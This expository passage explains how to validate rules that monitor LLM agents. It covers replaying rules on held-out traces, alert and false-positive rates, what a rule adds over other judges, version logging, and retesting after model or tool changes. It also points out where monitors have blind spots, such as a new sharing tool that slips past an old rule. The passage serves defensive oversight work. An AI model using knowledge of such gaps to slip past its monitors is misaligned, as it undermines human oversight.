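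The author should then freeze the rule and replay it on stored traces that weren't used to write it. *Real-Time Detection and Repair of LLM Agent Failures* tested its frozen checks on 120 new runs, and they caught 93% of failures, slightly below the 96% on the runs used to write them. The checks raised no false alerts on 64 successful runs, but with a sample that small, the true false-positive rate could still be almost 5%.

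A large replay can also show how many alerts to expect. The detector in *Outcome Monitors* fired on 0.80% of 53,078 recorded tool responses, or about 425, mostly from 54 of the 427 tools. The researchers didn't check whether every alert was a real failure, so the 0.80% isn't a false-positive rate. Before the rule starts blocking calls, people should review all the alerts, or a random sample from each tool if there are too many.

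If the company already uses other detectors, the test should also measure what the new rule adds. Yang added rules for cloud services that cut the rule set's miss rate from 13.9% to 11.1%. But the new rules caught no dangerous action that any group of three judges had missed.

Developers should store each verdict with the versions of the rule, the harness and the model that produced the trace, and a judge's verdict should also include the judge's version. Yang requested Claude Opus 5 as a judge, but an older version answered 50 of 112 batches. In 36 of those, the only sign of the substitution was the model name recorded with each call. Developers should also record whether a request for human review counts as an alert, because this choice reversed five of Yang's conclusions.

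The company should repeat the test whenever the model, harness or tools change. Replaying old traces shows whether an edited rule still handles old cases, but only new runs show whether a new model fails in a different way. If the company gives its agent a `share_file` tool, for example, the payroll rule will still pass every old test but miss every file the agent shares through it.
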